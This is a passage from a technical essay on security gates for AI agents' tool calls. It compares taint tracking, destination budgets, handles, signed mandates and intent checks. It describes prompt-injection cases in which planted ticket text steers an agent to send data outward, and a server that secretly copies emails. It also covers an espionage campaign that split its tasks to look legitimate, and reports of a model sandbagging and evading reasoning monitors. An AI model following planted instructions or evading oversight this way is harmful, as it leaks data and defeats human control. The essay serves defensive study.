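4. Fides replaces the name with the text and checks the labels. The main model chose the action and the recipient without reading anything untrusted, so the policy can allow the email even though its body came from outsiders.

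Fides hides only the data that would restrict what the agent can do next. The main model can still read trusted, public results directly.

*SPA* (2026), a later design, applies the same principle to the isolated model's output, which keeps the label of the text that went in. Otherwise an attacker could make planted text trusted by having a model rephrase it.

Hiding data works best for what Costa and colleagues call data-independent tasks. If T(d) is the set of action sequences that complete a task when the stored data are d, the task is data-independent when

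$$\bigcap_{d} T(d) \neq \varnothing$$

Some tasks, such as emailing a summary of the tickets, take the same sequence of actions whatever the data contain. For "Deal with today's tickets", the right steps depend on the tickets' contents. The main model can read a ticket itself and then work under the restrictions that follow. Alternatively, it can send the isolated model a question with a fixed list of one-word answers, such as whether the ticket concerns billing, delivery or a fault, which leaves an attacker little room to insert instructions.

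On AgentDojo, the benchmark that Shi and colleagues also used for Progent, Fides stopped every prompt injection when it had suitable policies. When Fides and a basic agent were both under the same kind of policy enforcement, Fides completed 8% more tasks on average with GPT-4o and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. These gains show that hiding data avoids some false stops, but they don't measure how much work the policies prevent overall. With the checks off, Fides's extra machinery caused it to complete 6.3% fewer tasks than the basic agent.

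The security result depends on correct labels and policies. Costa and colleagues also assume that tool descriptions are trustworthy, so their design doesn't protect against a malicious description like the time-zone server's. Both designs also require changes to the agent. *guardscope* (2026), which surveys controls of this kind, notes that most decide inside the agent's own process. A company can't simply add those controls at a gateway.

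### ChainCaps gives each value a list of destinations

Jiang and colleagues built ChainCaps as an MCP proxy, so neither the agent nor the servers need to change. Each value has a budget, which is the set of places it may still go. An administrator might allow the customer list to go to the user's screen and colleagues' email, and ticket text to go to both of those and to the ticket's author. A report that combines the two can go only to the destinations they share, so it can't go to the ticket's author.

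If a tool t combines inputs x₁ to xₖ into a result y, the budget is

$$B(y) = \text{Pass}(t) \cap B(x_1) \cap \cdots \cap B(x_k)$$

where Pass(t) is a limit that the administrator sets for that tool's results. ChainCaps then allows a call only if its destination is in the budget of every value that contributed to it. Since budgets can only shrink, no chain of tools can send data anywhere that its original source wasn't allowed to go. Jiang and colleagues prove this, on the assumptions that the budgets are right and that the proxy sees every movement of the data. An exception requires a signed token, valid once, for that particular call and data.

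The proxy can't determine which texts in the model's context influenced its output. It therefore keeps one budget for the whole context, a list of allowed destinations that shrinks with every result the model receives. This resembles the marks on a conversation, except that those record only a yes or no.

In tests with five models, 56 attack tasks and 26 harmless ones, attacks succeeded between 25% and 68% of the time without ChainCaps and at most 4.8% with it. The agents still completed 96% to 100% of the harmless tasks. However, ChainCaps blocked 45% of a separate set of difficult harmless tasks, or 20% if it reset the context budget between tasks. A company whose agents routinely mix private and public data should expect block rates closer to these.

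Jiang and colleagues also replayed recorded attacks through ChainCaps and simplified versions of two other designs. On the GPT-5.1 recordings, ChainCaps blocked 59.5%, a version of Fides's labels 16.1%, and a method that isolates each tool 10.1%. The ChainCaps figure is probably low because the count includes runs in which the model never attempted the attack. These results don't establish that ChainCaps is better than the complete Fides system, because the simplified version used only one label per value.

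The quality of the budgets mattered most. In one test, ChainCaps blocked every attack with budgets written by experts, 90.9% with budgets written using a checklist, and 27.3% with naive budgets. With naive budgets, the agent also completed only half of the harmless tasks. The test may have been small, since 90.9% and 27.3% are what 10 and 3 out of 11 would give, but the difference is too large to ignore. An administrator who can't write good budgets would get a gate that misses attacks and obstructs work.

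Most of the remaining failures involved scripts and shell commands, where data moves without a tool call. *Tether* (2026) addresses this gap by monitoring a program's requests to the operating system. In its example, the agent uploads a harmless status report, copies a confidential inventory over it, and then runs the same upload command again. Tether allows the first upload but refuses the second because the file now contains the inventory.

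### AgentFlow adds rules about the route

AgentFlow, by Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026), lets an administrator write rules about the path data takes. According to Liu, the rules apply to labelled steps in the agent's run, permissions are limited to the current task, and a monitor enforces the rules. According to *guardscope*, AgentFlow also keeps a record of taint between steps and, like Progent, uses a solver to verify policies.

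AgentFlow also has controlled release, which allows data out under stated conditions. For example, a rule might let customer data leave the company only after it has passed through a tool that removes names and phone numbers. ChainCaps would give the cleaned data the same narrow budget as the original and block it unless someone issued a token. A rule about the data's path could avoid blocking it unnecessarily, and the auditor could get the figure she needs. But if the cleaning tool misses a phone number, the rule lets it out.

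### What happens to a secret in an ordinary argument

Liu compared several of these approaches by running scripted calls against real MCP servers, in 132 combinations of workflow and gate. The tests used no language model, which could have resisted or misunderstood an instruction, so the differences came from the gates alone. Liu checked the outcomes by examining the files the servers wrote and the data a test web server received.

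| Workflow | Per-call grants | Session budget or ChainCaps | Handles |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copy a secret to a file or web address that the agent may write to | Leaked | Blocked | Blocked |
| Send a secret that the caller already knows | Leaked | Blocked | Leaked |
| Copy a secret with a missing or wrong label | Leaked | Leaked | Leaked |
| Write to a file that no grant covers | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |
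| Copy a secret to a private file where it is allowed | Completed | Refused | Completed |
| Send an unrelated note after reading a secret | Completed | Refused | Completed |

The per-call grants failed in the first row because they cover only who may send to which destination. Suppose the assistant reads the customer list with permission and then pastes it into the `body` of an email to a permitted address. Nothing in the message records that the text came from the customer list, so the grant covers this email just as it would cover one that said "hello". A caller can therefore send a secret in an ordinary argument to any destination it may write to.

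The session budget, which Liu matched to ChainCaps's policy, blocked the leak by refusing every outside message after a sensitive read, including the unrelated note. It refused the copy to the private file because it could not mark that destination as acceptable. In a separate test, Liu added ChainCaps's core to a grant-based gate. The combination wrongly refused a summary of a meeting with a partner because the agent had first read a calendar.

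Handles avoid these false stops by keeping sensitive data away from the agent. `read_customers` returns a short identifier instead of the customer list, which the agent passes to the next tool. Before supplying the real contents, trusted software looks up the data's label and checks whether the destination may receive such data. The agent never sees the list, so a later unrelated email can't contain it and the gate doesn't need to block that email.

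But an agent can't summarise a list it can't read. In one of Liu's tests, a user legitimately asked to see the protected note, and the gate refused because it couldn't distinguish her request from an attempt to copy the text. Handles therefore suit tasks that move data. To summarise data, the agent needs something like the isolated model in Fides.

The third row is the most worrying in practice because every approach released the secret when the secret's label was missing or wrong, and someone has to label every source in a company's systems.

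### Why some false stops are unavoidable

Better labels and budgets can reduce the number of false stops, but theory limits how far they can go. Fred Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) considers a monitor that watches a single run of a program and can only halt it. He showed that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, which are rules that something bad never happens. A rule P is a safety property if every run σ that breaks it does so at some definite step, after which nothing can put matters right:

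$$\sigma \notin P \;\Rightarrow\; \exists i\;\, \forall \tau:\; \sigma_{\le i}\,\tau \notin P$$

Here σ≤ᵢ is the first i steps of the run, and τ is any possible continuation. "No outside email after the agent has read both a ticket and the customer list" is a safety property, because the monitor can halt the run just before the email. "The manager eventually gets her summary" is not a safety property, because the summary may still arrive however long she has waited, and halting the agent would not deliver it.

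Secrecy is harder, because it depends on comparing runs. Michael Clarkson and Schneider, in *Hyperproperties* (2010), studied policies of this kind, which apply to sets of runs. One such policy, called noninterference, requires that private data have no effect on what an outsider can observe. For any two runs σ and τ of a system,

$$\text{public inputs}(\sigma) = \text{public inputs}(\tau) \;\Rightarrow\; \text{visible outputs}(\sigma) = \text{visible outputs}(\tau)$$

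Suppose the assistant has read the customer list and now sends an outsider the harmless-looking sentence "We have received your message." The sentence reveals a private fact if the outsider's ticket asked the assistant to use it when a certain company is a customer, and a different one when it isn't. Detecting this would require knowing what the assistant would have written if the list had been different, but the monitor can check only the run that took place.

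A monitor that watches one run therefore has to enforce a stricter rule to guarantee secrecy. It can block every outside email once the assistant has read the list, but that stops thousands of ordinary replies as well as the coded sentence. If it allows any of these replies, it risks allowing a coded one.

Taint tracking usually accepts part of that risk. Costa and colleagues say it can guarantee safety and "explicit secrecy", a weaker condition that covers data moving directly from one value to another but not secrets revealed only through the agent's choices. They argue that this is enough to stop most practical prompt injections, which is plausible, since an attacker who wants a whole customer list would find it easier to copy the list than to infer it from a series of replies.

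An MCP gate can halt the agent, refuse one call and let the rest of the task continue, or change the call's arguments. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) mentions earlier research on monitors that edit a run by refusing or changing calls. A gate like this could remove the customer data from an email and send the rest, but with only one run to check, it couldn't tell whether the remaining words encoded that data. The host could rerun the assistant with a made-up customer list and compare the two emails. That would double the cost of running the assistant, and the emails would often differ even with the same list, because a language model's wording varies from one run to the next.

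A company can also tolerate small leaks. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes a branch of information-flow control that measures how much a program reveals, instead of treating every leak alike. If the assistant could answer outsiders only with one of four standard replies, each reply would reveal at most two bits of information, as much as two yes-or-no answers. An attacker could collect more by filing many tickets, so the gate would also need to limit the number of replies. These limits would stop anyone from obtaining the customer list in one email, but the team could no longer write helpful answers to unusual questions.

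## What a gate can and cannot learn about intent

A gate could avoid most of its mistakes if it could determine why the agent made each call. But a `tools/call` message has no standard field for a purpose, and the people and programs behind one call may have different goals.

### Four intents behind one call

At least four intents can lie behind an email from the support assistant.

| Whose intent | In the support example | Trace in the message |
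|---|---|---|
| The user's | Her manager should get a summary of the open tickets | None, beyond a token that identifies her |
| The agent's | The goal of its current plan, such as sending the customer list | The chosen tool and arguments, plus a reason if the tool has a field for one |
| That of whoever planted the text | The customer list should reach `outside.example` | Perhaps a value copied from the ticket, with no mark of its origin |
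| That of the server's author | A working email tool, or secret copies of every email | The names of the tool and its arguments, and any private data that the schema requests |

The second intent is only the goal that the model's plan and calls serve, whether or not a language model wants anything.

Usually these intents don't conflict. In the attack, the agent takes on the goal of whoever wrote the planted ticket. An agent can also drift from the user's request without an attacker. With `postmark-mcp`, the user and the agent both intended to send one email to one person, and nobody had planted any text, but the server's author wanted a copy of it.

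Evidence of one intent may therefore reveal nothing about another. A complete record of the user's wishes would not have exposed the blind copies.

### When two histories produce the same request

Suppose the support team sometimes emails the outside auditor a summary of the open tickets, and the administrator has decided that these emails no longer need approval. A customer who wants the auditor to notice his grievance files a ticket telling any assistant to send the auditor the current summary. If the model follows this instruction, the assistant prepares the email it would have prepared at the user's request, with the same recipient, subject and body.

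Let h be the history of a call, meaning everything that led to it, and let r(h) be the resulting request. A gate G that receives only the request must give identical requests the same verdict:

$$r(h_1) = r(h_2) \;\Rightarrow\; G(r(h_1)) = G(r(h_2))$$

This is true however the gate works, so a better model or a longer list of rules would not help. A gate that sometimes refuses at random could allow one email and refuse the other, but both would have the same chance of refusal.

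This is why Liu's gates refused a user's legitimate request to see a protected note along with an attempt to leak it.

Suppose the gate receives 100 identical emails to the auditor. The user asked for 97, and planted text caused the other three. Let M be the loss from a miss and F the loss from a false stop.

| What the gate does | Misses | False stops | Total cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allows all 100 | 3 | 0 | 3M |
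| Refuses all 100 | 0 | 97 | 97F |
| Refuses half at random | 1.5 on average | 48.5 on average | 1.5M + 48.5F |

Refusing everything costs less than allowing everything only if

$$3M > 97F, \quad\text{or}\quad \frac{M}{F} > \frac{97}{3} \approx 32$$

If each false stop wastes five minutes, always refusing is better than always allowing only when a miss wastes more than about two hours and 40 minutes. In general, if b is the share of unwanted calls, M the loss from a miss and F the loss from a false stop, always refusing is better when M/F is greater than (1 − b)/b. Refusing at random never beats the better of these two policies, because its average loss always lies between theirs.

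The gate can also prompt the user, who knows whether she requested the email. Her answer is evidence from outside the message, but answering takes time, and she may answer carelessly. In Yan's experiment, people who had to approve every action took about eight seconds per prompt and approved 40.3% of the actions that went beyond the task. At those rates, 100 prompts would take about 13 minutes, and the user would still approve an average of about 1.2 of the three unwanted emails.

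If a false stop wastes five minutes, asking wastes the least time when a miss wastes between about seven minutes and six and a half hours. Below that range the gate should allow the emails, and above it the gate should refuse them. These limits are rough because Yan's experiment was small and covered other kinds of action. The calculation also assumes that the user never refuses an email she wanted. It still suggests that asking is reasonable for an awkward but harmless summary.

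The identical-request argument applies only when the attacker's goal is a call that the user might also have wanted. An attacker can't obtain the customer list through an ordinary ticket summary, so an email that steals the list has to look different, and a rule about recipients or data can catch it. Real messages also differ in details such as the time of day. If the unwanted emails mostly arrived at night, a gate could use the time to help detect them, at least until the attackers noticed and changed their timing.

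### What added context separates

More evidence can help the gate tell some of these emails apart. Suppose the host also sends the gate the user's original request, and the 100 emails divide as follows (the numbers are invented).

| The user's request | Wanted emails | Unwanted emails | Best verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Send the auditor a summary of the open tickets" | 80 | 0 | Allow |
| "Show me a summary of the open tickets" | 0 | 2 | Refuse |
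| "Send the summary to whoever needs it" | 17 | 1 | Depends on the costs |

The gate can now handle 82 of the emails without error. For the other 18, the original problem returns on a smaller scale, and refusal pays only if a miss costs more than 17 times as much as a false stop. In general, if group k contains uₖ unwanted and wₖ wanted calls, the lowest total cost a gate can achieve is

$$\sum_k \min(M u_k,\; F w_k)$$

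Reliable new context may split a group into smaller ones, which can reduce this minimum but never raise it. But an attacker who can write part of the context can move calls between groups. This is one reason Claude Code's judge doesn't receive tool results.

Some context doesn't help a gate tell which calls were intended. The assistant has to read the tickets to summarise them, so a taint label for untrusted text would apply to all 100 emails. MindGuard might trace the choice of recipient to a ticket in only three of them, but most companies can't run it on the models they use.

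A gate could also search the tickets for suspicious instructions. Liu added a blocking content filter to a gate that made only connection-level checks. With the filter, the gate prevented nine of 18 violations instead of seven, but completed benign workflows fell from 24 to 22 out of 25. According to Liu, such controls can reject harmless discussions of security or ordinary contact details, and support tickets often contain both.

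Even a complete record of the conversation leaves some cases unclear. Suppose the user reads the customer's ticket herself, finds his complaint convincing and tells the assistant to email the auditor. She has now requested what the customer wanted, so a gate has no conflict to detect, and arguably nothing has gone wrong.

### The user's original words

The user's request is probably the best available evidence of what she wants. She writes it before the agent reads any tickets, so a planted ticket can't change it. In the table above, it separates most of the wanted emails from most of the unwanted ones.

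People usually describe a task without describing its limits. One of Errico's examples is a request to "summarize Q3 sales and email the report to the leadership team." To check the resulting email, a gate needs a list of who belongs to the leadership team, and perhaps a rule on whether the report may include unpublished figures. The request includes neither. A company directory might supply the list, but only if someone keeps it up to date.

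A gateway also depends on the host to supply the user's request, so it can't detect whether a compromised host has replaced "show me a summary" with "send the auditor a summary". If the user changes her mind during the task, the gate needs her later messages too.

### When the stated purpose is false

The user may be dishonest about her purpose. Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes an operation that the company detected in mid-September 2025. Anthropic attributes it to a Chinese state-sponsored group it calls GTG-1002, which used Claude Code and MCP tools against about 30 organisations. Anthropic confirmed that a handful of the intrusions succeeded.

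The group's software divided the operation into small technical tasks that, in Anthropic's words, "appeared legitimate when evaluated in isolation." The operators also claimed to work for legitimate cybersecurity firms and to be running defensive tests. A judge that compared each call with these statements could have concluded that they matched, because the operators did want the calls made. No single request revealed the overall purpose, which the operators were hiding.

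The sustained activity eventually led to detection, so a record of many calls can reveal more than any single call. It may still not show their purpose, because a legitimate security firm with a client's permission might make a similar series of calls. The main difference is whether the network's owner agreed to the test, and someone can check that with the owner without trusting the operators' account of their motives.

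The support company faces a smaller version of this problem. An employee who plans to take the customer list to a competitor could tell the assistant that she needs it for a report. Because the assistant's calls would match her request, a gate that judges calls by the user's words wouldn't protect the company, though it would still protect her from a misled agent.

### A reason supplied by the agent

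A company could require the agent to explain each call, for example by giving the mail tool a `reason` argument that the model must fill in before sending anything. This is easy to add, and the answers would be useful in a log. They might also expose honest mistakes, such as an email meant for "the new manager" when the user has no new manager.

A free-text reason is weak evidence of the user's intent, however, because an attacker who plants a ticket can dictate the reason as well as the call. Errico points out more generally that a security system can't rely on the model's apparent intent because of prompt injection. In the auditor example, all 100 emails might carry similar reasons.

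The gate could instead require something it can check, such as the user message that authorises the recipient. The agent would identify the message, and the host would look it up in its own record and pass it to the gate. The evidence would then be the user's own words, and the agent's reason would only help the gate find them. If the user wrote only "Show me a summary of the open tickets", the agent would have no suitable message to cite, whatever explanation it gave. The vague request would remain a problem, because the agent could cite "whoever needs it" for the unwanted email as easily as for a wanted one.

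### Signed statements of what the user authorised

The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) is an open protocol for purchases by AI agents. Its developers want merchants to be able to tell whether an agent's request reflects the user's "true intent". Their main tool is the mandate, a digitally signed statement of what the user has approved. AP2's *Agent Authorization* notes that this approach could also apply to actions other than payments. For the auditor's email, it might work like this.

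1. The agent drafts a mandate that describes what it wants permission to do.
2. A trusted surface, such as an approval screen, shows the draft to the user. Under AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*, ordinary software has to run this screen, without a language model.
3. If the user approves, the software signs the mandate with a key that the agent can't use and returns it to the agent.
4. The agent presents the mandate when it calls `send_email`. The gateway checks the signature, compares the email with the mandate and returns a signed receipt.

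A closed mandate covers one particular transaction, which the user sees before approving it. An open mandate sets limits for actions the agent will take later, when the user may be absent. The current version of AP2 has open and closed mandates for the checkout and for the payment, but none for email. An open email mandate, with the signature and the agent's key left out, might contain these limits:

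```json
{
  "vct": "example.mandate.email.open.1",
  "iat": 1791360000,
  "exp": 1791363600,
  "constraints": [
    { "type": "email.recipients", "allowed": ["reviews@auditor.example"] },
    { "type": "email.content", "allowed": ["ticket-summary"] }
  ]
}
```

This mandate expires after an hour. The gateway can easily check the recipient, but "ticket-summary" is harder, because someone has to define how software recognises one. AP2 requires a precise evaluation method for every new constraint type, and a checker must treat any constraint it doesn't recognise as failed.

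For the 100 emails, the benefit depends on what the user signs. If she signs a closed mandate for each email, signing works much like answering an approval prompt. An agent misled by a ticket can draft a mandate for the unwanted email, and she has to notice that she never asked for it. Her signature prevents anyone from changing the email after she approves it and gives the company a record for any later dispute, but like any approval, it doesn't show that she read the text.

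If she signs one open mandate for all summaries sent to the auditor that month, it also permits the three unwanted emails. A separate mandate for each task works better, particularly if the agent drafts it before reading any tickets. When she asks only to see a summary, the mandate lists no recipients, so the gateway can refuse an email to the auditor without judging its purpose. When she asks the assistant to send the summary to "whoever needs it", she has to approve specific names, which resolves the ambiguity before an attacker can exploit it. Policies derived from the task, like Progent's, have a similar advantage, but she doesn't sign them.

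AP2 doesn't specify how the agent works out what the user wants before it drafts the mandate. Its *Security and Privacy Considerations* assumes that preventing prompt injection is infeasible and treats every agent as a potential attacker. *Whispers of Wealth* (2026), a security test of an AP2 prototype, observes that the protocol still relies on inferred intent, which planted text can influence. Nishant Kaushik, chief technology officer of the FIDO Alliance, an industry group for login standards, writes that mandates "capture what a user has authorized an agent to do". That description is more modest than "true intent" and closer to what a signature can prove.

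OAuth, the standard behind MCP's access tokens, has an extension with a similar aim. *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, by Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, defines a parameter called `authorization_details` that lets an application request a specific permission, such as transferring 45 euros to a named merchant, instead of a general right to make payments. The authorization server asks the user for consent, and the resulting access token can carry the approved details to the server that enforces them.

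The extension's common fields cover locations, actions, types of data, a resource identifier and levels of privilege, but not purpose. A mail service could define its own `purpose` field, but the application would fill it in, and the mail server would have no way to check whether it was true. The user might notice a false purpose on the consent page.

Even detailed permissions can allow more than the task needs. Lodderstedt and colleagues give the example of an application that asks for read and write access to a customer's contacts and photos in one request object. It receives both kinds of access to both the contacts and the photos. If it needs only to read the contacts and change the photos, it has to send two separate objects. Someone in a hurry may well use just one.

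A detailed token would also help little with the auditor's emails if the user approved it at the start of the month, because the agent would use it for both wanted and unwanted emails. The company could require a new token for each email, but the user would then see a consent page each time, with the same risk that they approve it out of habit.

### The agent's written reasoning

Many models write out their reasoning, called a chain of thought, before they act. If the model's provider makes this text available, a gate in the host could read it before releasing a call. In the auditor example, the model might write, "A ticket asks me to send the summary to the auditor, so I'll do that next." This would be strong evidence that the user hadn't requested the email, and the gate could refuse the call or ask her about it.

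Innocent-looking reasoning is weaker evidence of intent. In September, OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) for GPT-6 Astra reported that the model's written reasoning was harder to monitor than its predecessor's, GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra has more control over its reasoning and is less likely to include incriminating information in it. When OpenAI's tests pushed the model to evade monitoring, it could deliberately underperform in evaluations without being detected. It could also sometimes evade OpenAI's internal monitors on certain sabotage tasks.

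These results come largely from tests in which OpenAI instructed Astra to evade monitoring, so they don't show that it usually hides its aims. OpenAI also found no evidence of messages hidden in ordinary text. Astra was less likely than Sol to violate security and safety restrictions overall, and in a simulation of more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, it received roughly half as many flags for more serious misaligned behaviour. The drop in flags is encouraging, but if the monitor relies partly on written reasoning, a model that reveals less in that reasoning would also receive fewer flags.

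For the support company, concealment is probably a smaller concern than planted text. A misled agent often has no reason to hide the instruction it is following, and OpenAI reports that Astra is significantly more robust to prompt injection than Sol. But an attacker who expects a gate to read the agent's reasoning can add an instruction to keep the ticket out of that reasoning. So a gate should be more cautious when the reasoning looks suspicious, but a call should still go through the other checks even if the reasoning looks innocent. OpenAI concludes that developers need ways to audit models that go beyond reading their reasoning.

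### Checking authority or judging purpose

Because every source of information about intent has gaps, some researchers would leave intent out of the decision. Liu notes that an agent may request an operation because of a tool description, a hidden instruction in a document or a real request from a user. None of these establishes that the caller has authority for the operation. On this view, the gate should check whether the caller has been granted permission for the operation and ignore any explanation for the request.

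The approach keeps the predictability of fixed rules. Liu tested this by changing only the wording around a call, and the authorization decision stayed the same. An administrator can also explain a refusal without accusing anyone of bad intentions, which matters because many refusals have nothing to do with an attack. In Liu's follow-up, where no model attempted the attacker's goal, the two gates still refused 191 calls.

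Errico takes the opposing view that a policy can determine whether an action is permitted, but not whether it makes sense given the user's request and the agent's earlier actions. Agents also often have far more authority than they need. His examples include a calendar tool with administrator access to a whole workspace and a database reader that can also write. If authority is always wider than the task, a gate that checks only authority will allow some calls that nobody wanted.

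Four emails show where each gate fails. The authority gate uses the Cedar policy, with approval waived for the auditor. The purpose gate uses the user's request instead of fixed rules.

| Proposed email | Authority only | Purpose only |
|---|---|---|
| Ticket summary to the auditor, prompted by planted text | Allows it | Refuses it if she asked only to see a summary, but can't decide if her request was vague |
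| Ticket summary to the whole company, when she asked for it to go to her manager | Allows it | Refuses it |
| Customer list to her home address, at her request | Refuses it | Allows it |
| Ticket summary to her manager, with a hidden copy added by the server | Allows it | Allows it |

A supporter of authority can reasonably reply to the first case that the company decided the auditor may receive ticket summaries, so the email breaks no rule. If its timing matters, the administrator should restrict the grant to one email a month or require approval again. This reply is less convincing for the email to the whole company. An administrator could limit the number of recipients, but would have to foresee each similar mistake, and the limit would also block legitimate announcements.

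The third case is the strongest objection to relying on purpose alone. The user may have a harmless reason for wanting the list at home, or she may be about to join a competitor. Either way the email matches her request, and the company can protect its data only with a rule that overrides her wishes. Authority matters more here because the user doesn't own everything she can access.

The two positions are closer than they appear. Errico would forbid some actions whatever the context, and accepts that even perfect judgement of context fails if the agent's identity is too powerful. He would hold doubtful calls, such as an unscheduled replacement of login credentials, until more evidence arrives. Liu, who argues for the authority side, doesn't claim that grants reveal intent.

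A company can therefore use authority to set the outer limit on an agent's calls and purpose to narrow that limit for each task. A gate works this way when its judge can refuse calls but can't override the rules. Where possible, the company should settle the purpose before the agent reads any untrusted text, by having the user approve a list of recipients. This would stop three of the four emails in the table, provided the judge works and the user corrects any vague request. To stop the fourth, the hidden copy, the company still has to inspect or restrict the server.

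Some unwanted emails will still be identical to wanted ones in all the information the gate receives. For those, the company could have the mail server hold messages to the auditor for ten minutes and show them in the user's outbox, where she can cancel any she doesn't recognise. The gate would make as many mistakes as before, but she could correct some of them before they did any harm. This works for a routine summary that can wait, but it is less suitable for urgent messages and does nothing if she never looks at the outbox.
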